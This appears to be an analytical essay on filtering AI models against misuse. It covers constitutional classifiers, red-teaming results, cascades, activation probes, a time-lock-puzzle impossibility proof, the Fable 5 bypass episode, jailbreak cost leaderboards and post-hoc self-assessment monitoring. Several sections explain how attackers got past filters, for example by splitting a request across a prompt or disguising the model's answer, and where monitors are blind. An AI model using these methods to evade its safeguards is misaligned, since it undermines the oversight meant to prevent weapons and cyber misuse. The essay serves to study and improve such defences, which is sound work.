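The input filter checks the prompt before the model answers. The output filter checks the reply as the model writes it, updating its score at every token, and cuts the reply off if the score passes a threshold. Users can therefore start reading a reply before it is finished.

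This means that the output filter has to judge unfinished replies, although each training example has only one label y for the whole reply. For a reply of T tokens, training minimises

λ · L_NTP + Σ L_BCE( y, p(harmful | first T′ tokens) ),

where the sum runs over every length T′ from 1 to T. L_BCE is the penalty for assigning a low probability to the correct label. L_NTP is the usual penalty for predicting the next token badly, which helps to stabilise training, and λ sets its weight. As training went on, Sharma and colleagues gradually replaced each probability with the highest one so far in the reply. This matches how the filter works in practice, since a reply that has been cut off stays cut off.

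The method applies a form of adversarial training to the filters. If a new threat appears, developers can add it to the constitution, generate new examples and retrain the filters without changing the main model.

### Three thousand hours on a prototype

Sharma and colleagues invited 405 people to red-team (attack in order to test) a prototype, and about 183 took an active part. They tried to get answers to ten forbidden questions and could earn up to $15,000 for a universal jailbreak. The team's central estimate of the time participants spent red-teaming was 4,720 hours (90% confidence interval 3,242 to 7,417), so the often-quoted figure of 3,000 hours is cautious.

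None of the 113 reports answered all ten questions with even half the detail that a model without safeguards would give. No report answered more than five questions in full detail, and no person answered more than six across all their reports. Many of the better scores came from exploiting the automatic grader, for example with very long answers that happened to include enough of the expected terms.

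The prototype was also unusable as a product, because it refused about 44% of ordinary traffic on Claude.ai. The figures of 23.7% extra compute and 0.38% extra refusals belong to a later system, which covered only chemical weapons and used smaller filters and a longer list of permitted content. The 3,000 hours of red-teaming tested the prototype, so they are not evidence about this later system. In automated tests, jailbreaks succeeded 86% of the time against Claude without filters and 4.4% of the time with the later system's filters. When Sharma and colleagues combined the improved method with the prototype's wider constitution, the resulting system refused about 1.74% of traffic.

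The 0.38% increase is uncertain. It amounts to about 19 extra refusals in a sample of 5,000 conversations, and Anthropic acknowledges that it was not statistically significant.

In February 2025 Anthropic invited the public to try to make a filtered version of Claude 3.5 Sonnet answer eight questions about chemical weapons. Over a week, 339 people spent roughly 3,700 hours on more than 300,000 exchanges. Nobody succeeded on all eight questions in the first five days, but four participants did in the last two. Anthropic judged one of their methods a universal jailbreak and another a borderline case.

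The challenge was easier than a real attack in two ways. Participants learned immediately from an automatic grader whether an answer was good enough, whereas a real attacker could find out only by trying to follow the instructions. Anthropic also left the filters unchanged all week, although in normal use it could have updated them or investigated people who kept triggering them. But a real attacker may have much longer than the week participants had.

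A filter also protects only the traffic that passes through it. During the first programme, a software error let participants receive up to 128 more tokens after the output filter had flagged a reply, which made one report briefly look like a universal jailbreak. In August 2026, *Anthropic ran 133 million contractor chats with its bioweapon filters off* (Constantin, 2026) reported a much larger gap, in which the filters had not been running on contractors' exchanges for eleven months. Red-teaming the filters themselves would not have revealed this.

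### Filters that see only half an exchange

Cunningham, Wei and colleagues (2026), in *Constitutional Classifiers++*, attacked the first design further and found it was vulnerable because the input filter checked only the prompt and the output filter checked only the reply. Attackers could spread a forbidden request through a long, harmless-looking prompt and have the model put it back together. They could also have the model disguise its answer so that it looked harmless unless read alongside the prompt.

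These disguises also make the model less capable. Cunningham and colleagues tested two of them on GPQA Diamond, a set of difficult science questions. Claude Opus 4's accuracy fell from 74.2% to 32.3% with one and to 49% with the other. An attacker may therefore get past the filters and still receive poor instructions. But the gap between the two results worried the researchers, because it suggests that other disguises might reduce performance less.

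The remedy was an exchange classifier, which reads the reply together with the prompt. It needed no special training, since the existing input filter worked well when given both. It used about 50% more compute than the old pair of filters, because a larger model now had to read the replies.

Cunningham and colleagues compared the two designs by counting high-risk vulnerabilities, meaning attacks that got the model to answer more than five of eight questions with at least half the detail of an unguarded model. Red-teamers found 13 in 695,000 queries against the old design (0.0187 per thousand) and 2 in 226,000 against the exchange classifier (0.0088 per thousand). Anthropic's summary of the work, *Next-generation Constitutional Classifiers*, describes this as cutting successful attempts by more than half.

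The counts are too small to establish that. If successes are rare and independent, the number k found in a given amount of testing follows a Poisson distribution,

P(k) = e^(−μ) μᵏ / k!,

where μ is the number one would expect on average. A 95% confidence interval contains the values of μ that would not make the observed count surprisingly high or low. For a count of 13 it runs from 6.9 to 22.2, and for a count of 2 from 0.24 to 7.2. Dividing by the number of queries gives

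- 0.010 to 0.032 per thousand for the old design
- 0.001 to 0.032 per thousand for the exchange classifier.

The second interval contains nearly all of the first, but overlapping intervals don't rule out a real difference. If both designs were equally robust, we would expect the exchange classifier to have about 3.7 of the 15 successes, because it received about a quarter of the queries. It would have two or fewer about 25% of the time by chance.

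Even these intervals are too narrow, because the thousands of related queries that one person may send while refining an idea are not independent trials. Other evidence favours the new design. Four attacks on the old design got answers to all eight questions at half detail, after an average of 27 hours' work by the attackers' own accounts, while the only such attack on the exchange classifier took 100 hours. The explanation for the improvement is also convincing, since a filter that sees the whole exchange has information that the old filters lacked, but the size of the improvement remains unknown.

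### A cheap filter in front of an expensive one

Most conversations have nothing to do with weapons, so running the best classifier on all of them wastes computation. Cunningham and colleagues therefore used a cascade, in which a smaller exchange classifier checks every exchange and sends only the ones it flags to a larger classifier. The smaller classifier can raise many false alarms without annoying users, because it doesn't block the exchanges it flags.

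The first filter cost about a third as much per exchange as the second and passed on about 10% of traffic. If the second costs 1 unit, the average cost is

1/3 + 0.10 × 1 ≈ 0.43 units,

and the first filter accounts for about 77% of it. With a newer underlying model and more efficient software as well, the cascade cost 5.4 times less than the single exchange classifier.

The weakness of a cascade is that the second filter never checks what the first one lets through. If the first catches 95% of harmful exchanges and the second catches 90% of those, the cascade catches 85.5%, and a perfect second filter would raise that only to 95%. *A Layered Input-Output Defense for Open-Weight Language Models under Adaptive Jailbreak Attack* describes a much simpler system that first used a classifier to decide which prompts needed protection. The classifier passed 116 of 300 harmful requests as safe, and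 those accounted for 73% of all successful attacks, so the designers removed it. Cunningham and colleagues set their first threshold low enough to flag the vast majority of the attacks from their own red-teaming, but this can't show how the filter would treat new kinds of attack.

Bounty hunters found five high-risk vulnerabilities in the cascade in 569,000 queries, but none of their attacks drew out answers to every question as detailed as an unguarded model's. According to a footnote in the paper, expert red-teamers outside the bounty programme did discover universal jailbreaks for this system, with substantial effort and automated tools. The bounty programme's failure to find one therefore reflected the limits of its attackers as well as the strength of the filters. The American and British AI institutes also tested several versions of these systems before Anthropic released Claude Opus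 4 and 4.1, according to Anthropic's *Strengthening our safeguards through collaboration with US CAISI and UK AISI*.

### Filtering with the model's own activations

The final version made the first filter cheaper still. A language model has to compute activations in order to write a reply, and a linear probe can reuse them. At each token t, the probe multiplies the activations by learned weights and adds up the results:

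p(harmful | tokens so far) = σ(Wᵀψₜ + b).

Here ψₜ is the list of activations from all the model's layers at that token, W holds one weight for each activation, and b is a constant. The function σ(z) = 1/(1 + e^(−z)) turns the total into a probability. The simple cat classifier uses the same kind of weighted sum, but of pixels instead of activations.

Cunningham and colleagues calculate how much computation filtering takes with Gemma 3, a family of open models. A probe on the 27-billion-parameter model takes about 377,000 operations per token. Running a separate 4-billion-parameter model as a filter takes about 8 billion, about 20,000 times as many.

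A single word can produce a misleadingly high score, so they averaged the totals over the last M = 16 tokens during training:

z̄ₜ = (1/M) Σ (Wᵀψₜ₋ₖ + b), for k = 0 to M − 1.

Suppose that one token scores 8 and the fifteen before it score −2 each. The last token's score alone would give a 99.97% probability of harm. Averaging all sixteen scores gives (8 − 30)/16 ≈ −1.4, or a probability of about 20%, so a filter that looks for consistent signs of harm would let the reply continue. In use, the probe keeps a running average in which older tokens gradually count for less, because this requires storing only one number.

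Training has to deal with another problem. Two replies may begin with the same harmless paragraph, after which one turns harmful. If every token counted equally, the probe would see the same paragraph labelled harmful in one example and harmless in the other, and would learn to give it a probability of about 50%. Cunningham and colleagues therefore weighted the error at each token by

wₜ = exp(z̄ₜ/τ) / Σₛ exp(z̄ₛ/τ),

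where τ controls how strongly the weight concentrates on the highest scores. The harmless opening has a low score and therefore little weight, so the probe can treat it as harmless without penalty. A confident alarm in a harmless reply has a large weight, which is appropriate because one such alarm would cut off the reply.

On about 7,000 stored red-teaming exchanges, the best probe let through roughly 1.4% of attacks. It did better than the smaller of the two external classifiers and almost as well as the larger one. Combining the probe with the larger classifier worked better than using either alone, and better than combining the two external classifiers. The external classifiers' scores were more correlated with each other than with the probe's, so the probe tended to make different mistakes.

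In the production system, the probe monitors every exchange and passes those that score above a threshold to the external classifier. The final score for these exchanges is 0.55 times the probe's score plus 0.45 times the classifier's. Cunningham and colleagues ran this system on real Claude Sonnet 4.5 traffic in December 2025. The probe passed on about 5.5% of the traffic, and the full system flagged 0.05%. The system needed about 40 times less computation than the exchange classifier alone. In 1,736 hours of red-teaming, attackers found one high-risk vulnerability and no universal jailbreak.

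The table gives their figures for all four systems, with Poisson intervals calculated from the counts.

| System | High-risk vulnerabilities / queries | Per thousand queries (95% interval) | Compute relative to the old design | Traffic refused |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate input and output filters | 13 / 695,000 | 0.019 (0.010–0.032) | 100% | 0.073% |
| Exchange classifier | 2 / 226,000 | 0.009 (0.001–0.032) | 150% | 0.038% |
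| Two-stage cascade | 5 / 569,000 | 0.009 (0.003–0.021) | 27.8% | 0.036% |
| Probe and classifier | 1 / 198,000 | 0.005 (0.0001–0.028) | 3.5% | 0.050% |

The saving in computation is large and doesn't depend on a handful of events. The evidence on robustness is stronger when the three newer systems are pooled, which gives 8 successes in 993,000 queries. If all four systems were equally robust, the newer three would do at least this well only about 4 or 5% of the time. But the programmes differed in their questions, rewards and guarded models, so this is suggestive at most.

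Anthropic also reports that refusals fell 87%, from 0.38% to 0.05%, but the 0.38% comes from the small sample in the 2025 paper. Cunningham and colleagues' own version of the old design refused 0.073% of production traffic, so the like-for-like drop is about a third. The final system refuses slightly more than the two intermediate ones.

### Fifty flags for each real case

A flag rate of 0.05% is one exchange in 2,000, which few users would notice. The rate is a poor measure of how many flags are correct, because that depends on how common harmful exchanges are. Nobody outside the company knows the true figure, but suppose it is one in 100,000. In 100,000 exchanges, the system would raise 50 flags, and even if it caught the one harmful exchange, the other 49 would be false alarms.

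In general, the share of flags that are correct is

(share of harmful exchanges × share of those caught) / flag rate.

With the figures above, this is (0.00001 × 1)/0.0005 = 2%. If the filter catches only half the harmful exchanges, it is 1%. If harmful exchanges were ten times as common, it could reach 20%.

If only 2% of flagged exchanges are harmful, blocking the replies may still be acceptable, because 49 out of every 50 users blocked can rephrase their harmless questions, and the one harmful answer might have been very dangerous. A 2% hit rate would be a poor basis for banning someone or reporting them to the police. At its low threshold, the probe passes on 5,500 of every 100,000 exchanges for further checking, and too many of these are harmless for it to block anything by itself.

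False alarms also affect some users more than others. Sharma and colleagues found that the increase in refusals was more noticeable on questions about chemistry, and Cunningham and colleagues found that the probe flagged harmless scientific requests more often than the external classifiers did. A chemist's harmless requests may therefore trigger the filter far more often than one time in 2,000.

Cascades have the same effect outside weapons filtering. In *Measuring Risk, Not Harm* (2026), a linear first stage checked chatbot conversations for signs of psychological harm and sent only 27% of cases to a language model judge. The cascade's flags were correct more often than those of the judge alone, but the judge alone caught more of the real cases.

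### A theoretical limit on weaker filters

A filter that runs on all traffic has to use less compute than the model it guards, which can be a fundamental weakness. Ball, Gluch and colleagues (2025) proved in *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* that, for some language models, no prompt filter that runs significantly faster than the model can tell certain harmful prompts from innocent ones.

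The proof uses a time-lock puzzle, which is quick to make but slow to solve. Take two large primes p and q, multiply them to get n, and choose a number r. The puzzle is to compute

r^(2ᵗ) mod n,

the remainder when r, squared t times in a row, is divided by n. Anyone who doesn't know p and q has to do the squarings one after another. Anyone who does know them can first reduce the exponent 2ᵗ to its remainder on division by (p − 1)(q − 1).

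For example, with p = 7, q = 11, r = 2 and t = 10, the exponent is 1,024. Dividing it by 60 leaves a remainder of 4, so the maker gets the answer, 2⁴ = 16, with two squarings instead of ten. With realistic numbers, the maker still finishes almost at once, while the solver may need billions of squarings.

In the proof, an attacker encrypts a forbidden request, using the solution to such a puzzle as the key. The attacker then hides the puzzle and the encrypted request in the random word choices of an ordinary-looking prompt. The model recovers both, solves the puzzle, decrypts the request and obeys it. The filter doesn't have time to solve the puzzle, so it can't tell the prompt from an innocent one. The result assumes that time-lock puzzles exist, meaning that nobody can shortcut the squarings, even with many computers working in parallel. Cryptographers generally consider this plausible,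 but nobody has proved it.

Ball and colleagues concede that the model in their proof is contrived. Someone has to build it to look for hidden puzzles, and there is no sign that ordinary chatbots do this. But they argue that weaknesses in cryptography have often looked artificial until someone exploited them, citing a 2016 attack on the Ethereum network that stole over $60 million. The theorem rules out a general guarantee that a fast external prompt filter will work for every model, but it doesn't show how likely such a filter is to fail on Claude.

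A further theorem shows that, for a specially constructed model and standard of harm, no efficient output filter can distinguish harmful outputs from safe ones, even if it runs for longer than the model. This is less relevant to weapons instructions, which an expert can usually recognise, than to something like a business plan whose harm appears only when someone carries it out.

The results don't rule out other defences. A filter as capable as the model could solve the puzzle too, although Ball and colleagues ask why anyone would then trust the filter more than the model. The theorems also don't cover filters with access to the model's internal computations. In the prompt construction, the model has to decrypt the forbidden request before obeying it, so such a filter might detect the request at that point.

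The attacks on half-exchange filters used no cryptography, but they resemble this result because they relied on the model interpreting something the filter could not. Zhang, Xia and colleagues (2026), in *Scaling Misuse Detection with Self-Assessment*, reduce this gap by having the guarded model assess each conversation after it has replied. They tested this on Claude Fable 5, which Anthropic launched with cybersecurity filters and later redeployed. At a false-positive rate of 1%, the model flagged 78% of the conversations that a stronger classifier labelled potentially harmful, and 94% of the high-priority ones.

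Self-assessment needs little extra computation because the model has already processed the conversation, and it should improve as models do. But if one conversation in 100,000 were harmful, a false-positive rate of 1% would produce about 1,000 false alarms for each real case, so self-assessment is better suited to finding patterns of misuse for further investigation than to blocking replies. The attacker's text is also still in the model's context when it makes the assessment, so a prompt that misled it once might do so again.

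### What the probes respond to

Linear probes improved the filters and greatly reduced the compute they needed, but the researchers didn't identify which internal computations distinguish harmful exchanges from harmless ones, or what would make that difference disappear.

Anthropic compares the probe's signal to Claude's "gut intuitions" and argues that attackers will find internal activations harder to manipulate than outputs. This is plausible if attackers can only send prompts and read replies. But Cunningham and colleagues tested the probe alone only on stored attacks, which were developed without the probe in place. The adaptive red-teaming targeted the combined system, so it doesn't show how much of the robustness came from the probe.

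The probes tested in *Linear Probes Transfer from Base to Distilled Language Models despite Rotation* (Tsatsos, 2026) evidently detected something beyond alarming words, but they still responded partly to how harmful a request appeared. Tsatsos compared probes on four open models with a classifier that saw only the text of the prompt, using AUC, the chance that a randomly chosen harmful prompt scores higher than a randomly chosen harmless one. On XSTest, where harmless prompts deliberately contain alarming words, the probes beat the text classifier by 0.15 to 0.20. On a second set of prompts, the advantage was between 0.03 and 0.20, and the probes flagged 29% to 42% of the harmless requests that sounded harmful.

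These small probes, trained on 450 prompts, were far simpler than Anthropic's, so their error rates don't apply to Anthropic's probes. Comparing a production probe with a text-only classifier would be just as informative, and it requires no mechanistic understanding. Tsatsos also applied the probes without retraining to later models built from the same four. The direction separating safe from unsafe prompts had turned by 17° to 35°, yet the AUC on XSTest changed by at most 0.027. A developer can therefore sometimes reuse a probe on a changed model without knowing what the probe detects.

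Other researchers have also obtained good results from activations without explaining them much further. In *Safety Beyond the Interface* (2026), a neural network with only 12.6 million parameters read the activations of Llama-3.1-8B and scored 82.7% on a standard test of harmful content, where 100% would mean no misses and no false alarms. Two separate filter models, each with around 7 billion parameters, scored 84.4% and 86.7%.

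A mechanistic explanation of the probe might show why it flags harmless science questions and which disguises would keep a forbidden request from triggering it. So far, the improvements have come without one. Red-teamers' attacks exposed the blind spot between the two original filters, and anyone could understand it without looking inside a model. Cunningham and colleagues then improved the probe by averaging its scores, changing the training loss and adding more layers, and kept the changes that let fewer attacks through.

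## Fable 5: a filtered model withdrawn and released again

On 9 June 2026 Anthropic released Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5, which share one underlying model but have different safeguards. According to Anthropic's *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026), Mythos 5 can find and exploit software vulnerabilities better than any other model and all but the most skilled people. Anthropic gave it only to a few trusted partners in Project Glasswing, a defensive cybersecurity programme. Anyone could use Fable 5, because classifiers much like the Constitutional Classifiers limited access to its most dangerous capabilities. Three days after the release, the US government restricted both models because researchers at Amazon had bypassed Fable 5's safeguards.

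### The report, the controls and the repair

The Amazon researchers found a prompting method that made Fable 5 identify several software vulnerabilities. In one case it also wrote code showing how to exploit the flaw. Amazon invests in Anthropic and hosts its models. Tech Times' *Amazon Triggered Claude Fable 5 Shutdown* (2026), citing *The Wall Street Journal*, reported that Amazon's chief executive, Andy Jassy, alerted Treasury Secretary Scott Bessent.

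On 12 June the government applied export controls that barred foreign nationals from using either model, even inside the United States. Anthropic had no reliable way to check nationality in real time, so it suspended both models for everyone.

The government objected to the company's conduct as well as to the jailbreak. *Trump admin says Anthropic's 'recklessness' triggered export controls on latest AI models* (Lawrence, 2026) reports a senior official's complaint that Anthropic's handling of the weakness had damaged the government's trust. By 15 June cybersecurity experts were urging the government to lift the export controls, according to a headline listed beside *Anthropic's Fable 5 and Mythos 5 Are Back with New Security Guardrails* (Poireault, 2026).

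Anthropic called the jailbreak narrow. To show that it gave attackers nothing new, its staff gave the same tasks to weaker models. Claude Opus 4.8, GPT-5.5 and Kimi K2.7 could all find the vulnerabilities Amazon reported, and every model tested could write the same exploit, including the small Claude Haiku 4.5. These results are strong evidence about the vulnerabilities Amazon reported but weaker evidence of what else the technique could have done, since a prompt that gets Fable 5 to look for easy flaws might also get it to look for flaws that weaker models would miss. Anthropic states that the technique exposed no abilities unique to Mythos, but the comparison with weaker models can't establish that.

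Anthropic then worked with the government on a new classifier aimed at the behaviour in the report. On 26 June the government let a set of US organisations use Mythos 5 again, and on 30 June, after a review, the Commerce Department lifted the controls on both models (Miller, 2026, *Trump administration lifts Claude Mythos 5, Fable 5 export restrictions*). Fable 5 returned worldwide the next day.

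Fable 5's return came with conditions. According to the Center for AI Safety's *AISN #76*, a letter from Commerce Secretary Howard Lutnick reportedly states that Anthropic agreed to look proactively for security risks in its models, collaborate on future releases and tell the government about malicious activity. In a similar case, OpenAI limited its new GPT-5.6 models to a small group of partners on 26 June at the government's request, but said such a process should not become the long-term default.

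### What "over 99%" covers

Anthropic says that the new classifier blocks the technique in Amazon's report more than 99% of the time. In a very small fraction of cases, the model may still give information, though too little to help an attacker. The Center for AI Safety said the system blocks jailbreak attempts with high accuracy, which is a broader claim than Anthropic's. The figure comes from a fixed test against one known technique, a kind of test that defences usually pass. It does not measure how often the classifier would stop an attacker who changes the technique after being blocked.

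Repetition matters too. If exactly 1% of attempts got through and each attempt were independent, an attacker who tried 100 times would succeed at least once with probability

1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 63%.

The real chance may be much lower, because the failures may be concentrated on a few requests and Anthropic may notice someone who triggers the filter 99 times.

Anthropic also reports that researchers at the Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), part of the Commerce Department, tested the safeguards and agreed that they were "extraordinarily strong". This assessment covers both the old and new safeguards. Amazon's researchers had got past the old ones, so the assessment is little help in judging how much the repair improved the safeguards.

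Anthropic's post doesn't explain why the old classifier let the requests through. The wording may have made any cybersecurity request look harmless, or the classifier may have treated this kind of bug-hunting as routine work. The first fault would be much more serious, because the same wording might then work for attacks on power grids. Testers could find out which fault it was, without looking inside the classifier, by trying the same wording with other forbidden requests. A mechanistic explanation could help if it predicted which other wordings would have the same effect.

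### The safety margin

A classifier gives each request a score, and its developers choose the threshold above which requests are blocked. Anthropic deliberately sets the threshold low enough to block many requests that are probably harmless. It calls this band of requests the safety margin, and made it much wider for Fable 5 than for any earlier model.

Invented numbers can illustrate the effect. Suppose that harmless requests have an average score of 0 and harmful ones an average of 3, that both sets of scores follow a bell curve with a standard deviation of 1, and that a jailbreak lowers the score of every harmful request by 1.

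| Threshold | Harmless requests blocked | Harmful requests missed | Harmful requests missed with the jailbreak |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 2.3% | 15.9% | 50% |
| 1 | 15.9% | 2.3% | 15.9% |
| 0 | 50% | 0.1% | 2.3% |

When the threshold is low, the jailbreak mostly lets through requests that scored just above it, which are the blocked requests least likely to do harm. Anthropic classes every jailbreak of Fable 5 reported by the end of June, including Amazon's, as minor in this sense. It distinguishes these from narrow harmful jailbreaks, which let through one dangerous behaviour, and universal ones, which let through a whole class of them. The margin protects much less against an attack that greatly lowers the scores of the most dangerous requests.

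How wide the margin should be depends on the costs of the two mistakes. Let p be the probability that a request is harmful, H the cost of answering a harmful request and c the cost of blocking a harmless one. Blocking is the better choice when

p × H > (1 − p) × c, or p > c / (c + H).

If a harmful answer is 10,000 times as bad as a needless block, the developer should block anything with more than about a 0.01% chance of being harmful. Nearly everything the filter blocks near that threshold will be harmless, which can infuriate the people affected even if the policy is right.

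Anthropic also reduced c. When a classifier blocks a request to Fable 5, the system notifies the user and sends the request to a weaker model, so most people still get an answer. Mistaken blocks therefore do less harm, which justifies a lower threshold and is one reason the margin could be so wide. But someone who pays for Fable 5 may often get the weaker model's answer instead.

### What the margin cost users

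Anthropic admitted that the classifier which ended the export controls flagged harmless requests even more often during routine coding and debugging.

*Improving Fable 5's biology safeguards* (2026) explains that Anthropic launched the model with a filter that blocked almost all biology questions. The company's tests suggested that Fable 5 could give significant help to someone developing a biological weapon, and harmful work in biology can look very much like useful work. For example, scientists who make a live vaccine have to grow the pathogen it protects against, and the blood-pressure drug captopril came from research on snake venom. Waiting for a more precise filter would have delayed the whole model by weeks or months, so Anthropic chose to release it to non-biologists first.

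On 7 August Anthropic replaced the biology filter. It had rewritten the constitution (the list of permitted and forbidden content) to describe harmless uses in much more detail, asked experts inside and outside the company to comment, and retrained the classifier on new examples. In its tests, the new filter sent about 85% fewer biology requests to a weaker model. People asking about lab results, symptoms or coursework should now rarely notice the filter. Requests about virology, toxicology and molecular design still go to the weaker model, so Fable 5 remains unusable for professional biology research and drug development.

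A developer can get such a fall by raising the threshold, which lets more harmful requests through, or by making the classifier better at telling harmful requests from harmless ones, which doesn't have to let more through. In the invented example, suppose retraining raises the average harmful score from 3 to 4. The developer can then move the threshold from 1 to 2, block 86% fewer harmless requests and still miss only 2.3% of harmful ones. Anthropic attributes its result to better discrimination, which is believable given the detailed work on the constitution. But the 85% figure covers all diverted requests, including any that were rightly diverted. Anthropic says only that the new classifier still "generally" triggers on harmful requests, without giving a rate, so outsiders can't calculate how much the change weakened security, if at all.

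The improvement came from a better description of what people legitimately ask. This required expertise in biology and many examples, but it did not require understanding how Fable 5 or its classifier works internally.

### A scale for the severity of jailbreaks

The June dispute was partly about how severe the jailbreak was, and the two sides had no agreed way to measure that. Anthropic has since begun drafting a severity scale with Amazon, Microsoft, Google and other Glasswing partners. Two of its criteria concern what the attacker gains, and two concern how soon the jailbreak could cause harm. Anthropic's post doesn't score Amazon's bypass, but it gives enough information to attempt a partial score.

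| Criterion | What earns a high score | Amazon's bypass |
|---|---|---|
| Capability gain | Help well beyond existing tools, even for experts | Low on the evidence published, since weaker models could do the same |
| Breadth | One technique works for many kinds of attack | Probably low, with several vulnerabilities found but only one exploit |
| Ease of weaponisation | Works on the first or second try, with little skill | Unknown |
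| Discoverability | Widely known and available online | Low at first, since specialists found it |

The last score is somewhat doubtful, because the researchers found the bypass and the government acted on it within three days of the release, which suggests that other capable teams could have found it quickly too. The score also changes over time, because a technique that takes specialists to discover is easy to copy once somebody posts it.

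The draft doesn't specify how to combine the four scores, which could change the verdict. If developers add them, a jailbreak that is easy to use and widely known could look fairly serious even if it adds no capability beyond what a free model provides. If they multiply them, a capability gain of zero makes the total zero. Multiplying seems closer to Anthropic's argument in June, but it also makes the total depend heavily on the capability estimate, which the developer is usually best placed to make and has an interest in keeping low.

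For the worst jailbreaks, such as one that someone is already using to cripple banks or power grids, Anthropic promises to start deploying countermeasures as soon as it confirms their severity. It is also setting up a team to watch for reports around the clock and has invited outside researchers to submit cyber jailbreaks of Fable 5. The scale only rates jailbreaks, so it doesn't address the official's complaint about how the company had behaved.

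### What it costs to break a model

Developers' own accounts of their safeguards are hard to compare, so FAR.AI, a nonprofit research group, ran the same attacks on four leading models and estimated what a universal jailbreak of each would cost. Its researchers broke known jailbreaks into components, wrote software that recombined them, and sent several hundred thousand prompts. FAR.AI's *Introducing the AI Security Leaderboard* (2026) defines a universal jailbreak as one that works on more than three quarters of the harmful requests in a domain, such as chemical weapons or hacking.

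| Model | Estimated cost of a universal jailbreak |
|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | None found; above $14,000 if one exists |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | None found; above $14,000 if one exists |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | Under $300 |
| Grok 4.5 | $58 across all domains; $24 for cyber alone |

In the simplest model of such a price, if each candidate attack costs *a* dollars to try and a fraction *f* of candidates are universal jailbreaks, an attacker can expect to spend about *a*/*f* dollars to find one. Testers who find no universal jailbreak learn only that *f* is small, so they can give a lower limit for the price but no upper limit. The $14,000 figure also applies only to someone using FAR.AI's software. The researchers found that for some models, an expert who learned from each attempt could find about ten times as many universal jailbreaks.

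The gap between $58 and $14,000 is too large for details of the method to explain, so developers could do much better with existing techniques. Some of the successful attacks used components anyone could find online in about fifteen minutes. Even $14,000 is a small sum for a criminal group, let alone a government, and FAR.AI warns that its result is "a floor, not a clean bill of health". The three-quarters threshold also hides partial failures, because an attack that worked on 70% of requests would not count.

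FAR.AI published these results on 29 July, nine days before Anthropic narrowed its biology filter. The model it tested refused almost all biology questions, so someone would have to repeat the test on the more useful version to learn whether it is equally hard to break.

How much Fable 5's safeguards protect the public also depends on what other models allow. FAR.AI points out that an attacker refused by one model can go to another, so overall security depends heavily on the least protected model available. This is true for any task that model can do. The strongest models' safeguards still matter for tasks that only those models can do, because jailbreaking Grok 4.5 wouldn't give an attacker the same capability. The severity scale's first criterion is based on the same distinction.

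Gray Swan, a security company, instead measures the chance that a single attempt succeeds. Its *Frontier Hazard Tracker* gives these results for three models from November 2026. The last column is a calculation from the biological rates that assumes attempts are independent.

| Model | Chemical weapons, breaks per attempt | Biological weapons, breaks per attempt | Attempts needed for an even chance of a biological break |
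|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-6.2 Astra | 1.4% | 2.9% | 24 |
| GPT-6.2 Sol | 2.3% | 3.3% | 21 |
| Gemini 4 Neon | 5.7% | 6.2% | 11 |

In this test, a break is one harmful answer, which is far less than a strategy that works on most requests. The rates can't be converted into FAR.AI's dollar figures, so they don't show whether safeguards improved between July and November.

Attempts aren't independent in practice either. In Gray Swan's public contest from 16 to 27 November, 4,508 people made 5.7 million attempts, of which 2.8% succeeded. Only 1,179 people had any success, averaging about 133 successes each. The average success rate per attempt therefore understates the danger from skilled attackers and overstates it for everyone else. Success rates also varied by model, from 0.3% for GPT-6.1 Terra to 11.4% for Nemotron 3.5 Super VL.

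### Finding misuse afterwards

Anthropic also looks for misuse after the model has replied, using the self-assessment that Zhang and colleagues tested on Fable 5. A short hidden instruction at the end of the conversation has the model record whether the request was potentially harmful, the type of harm, how urgently a person should review it, and whether the model refused, with a one-sentence explanation. 凤凰网's *每条聊天记录都要秘密过审！Anthropic自曝新动作，Claude已开始全天候暗中监视用户* (2026), a Chinese news report, puts the extra computation below 2%, whereas some separate safety models use nearly a quarter of a system's computing power.

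To train Fable 5, Anthropic had a stronger model, Claude Mythos Preview, apply the full safety rules and write example assessments. Fable 5 learned to imitate these, and Anthropic then trained it with reinforcement learning that scored its format, categories and priorities. Its detection rates, 78% overall and 94% for high-priority conversations at a 1% false-positive rate, measure only agreement with a stronger classifier. If that classifier misses a kind of harm, the detection rates don't reflect it, and Fable 5 may well miss it too because it learned from a similar model.

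Across four model sizes, the share caught at the same false-positive rate rose with size from about 16% to 96%, according to 凤凰网. When researchers removed all examples of fraud from the training data, the model still caught at least 80% of fraud cases. It had evidently learned something more general than a list of forbidden topics, which matters for catching misuse that nobody has thought to list.

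Used as a live filter, self-assessment performed badly. It cut the success rate of attacks only from 79% to 54%, because an attacker who sees a refusal knows which message caused it and can try another. Anthropic therefore runs it silently and groups the flags by customer every night. The advantage of grouping follows from the arithmetic. Take a customer with 200 harmless conversations. At a 1% false-positive rate, the system raises about 2 flags, and the chance of 10 or more is roughly 1 in 25,000. If 20 of the 200 were harmful, it would raise about

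20 × 0.78 + 180 × 0.01 ≈ 17 flags.

A rule that sends any customer with ten flags to a human reviewer would catch nearly all customers of the second kind and very few of the first. This assumes that false alarms fall on customers at random. A security researcher who asks about exploits all day will trigger false alarms much faster. Anthropic lets administrators add a list of permitted work to the instruction.

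The system has found abuse that other tools missed. In one review it found more than 100,000 serious violations involving child abuse from a single business customer, which Anthropic reported to the US National Center for Missing and Exploited Children. But it detects abuse only after the model has answered, so it works best against people who need many conversations, such as scammers, and worst against someone who needs one good reply.

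It also requires someone to keep the conversations, which some business customers don't allow. In November, Anthropic began publicly testing a tool for these customers that looks for misuse spread across many requests while the data stays in the customer's own cloud (Kovacs, 2026, *Anthropic Expands Enterprise Safeguards for Detecting AI Misuse*).

### Several imperfect layers

Anthropic and OpenAI both rely on defence in depth, using several safeguards in the hope that an attack that passes one will fail at another. OpenAI's *Strengthening cyber resilience* argues that no system could prevent all misuse in cybersecurity without badly hampering defenders. OpenAI trains its models to refuse harmful requests, restricts who has access and what can leave its systems, and watches for threats from outsiders and its own staff. Its *Managing frontier AI risk* (November 2026) extends this approach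 over a model's whole life, with isolated test environments during research, close monitoring while only employees use the model, and blocking and monitoring after release.

The risks have grown since June. OpenAI's *Path to Astra* announced in September that Astra was the company's first model to reach its "Critical" level for cybersecurity. Given the right tools and access, such a model can find unknown flaws in many well-protected systems and work out how to exploit them without step-by-step human guidance. OpenAI's rules require stronger safeguards at that level.

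A second layer adds less protection if it fails on the same attacks as the first. If each of two layers misses 10% of attacks independently, both miss only 1%. If the second misses 60% of the attacks that got past the first, both miss 6%. Self-assessment is vulnerable to this problem because one prompt can mislead the model both when it replies and when it reviews the reply. O'Shei (2026), in *Claude self-assessment trades independence for context*, therefore expects companies to pair it with fixed controls that no model can override.

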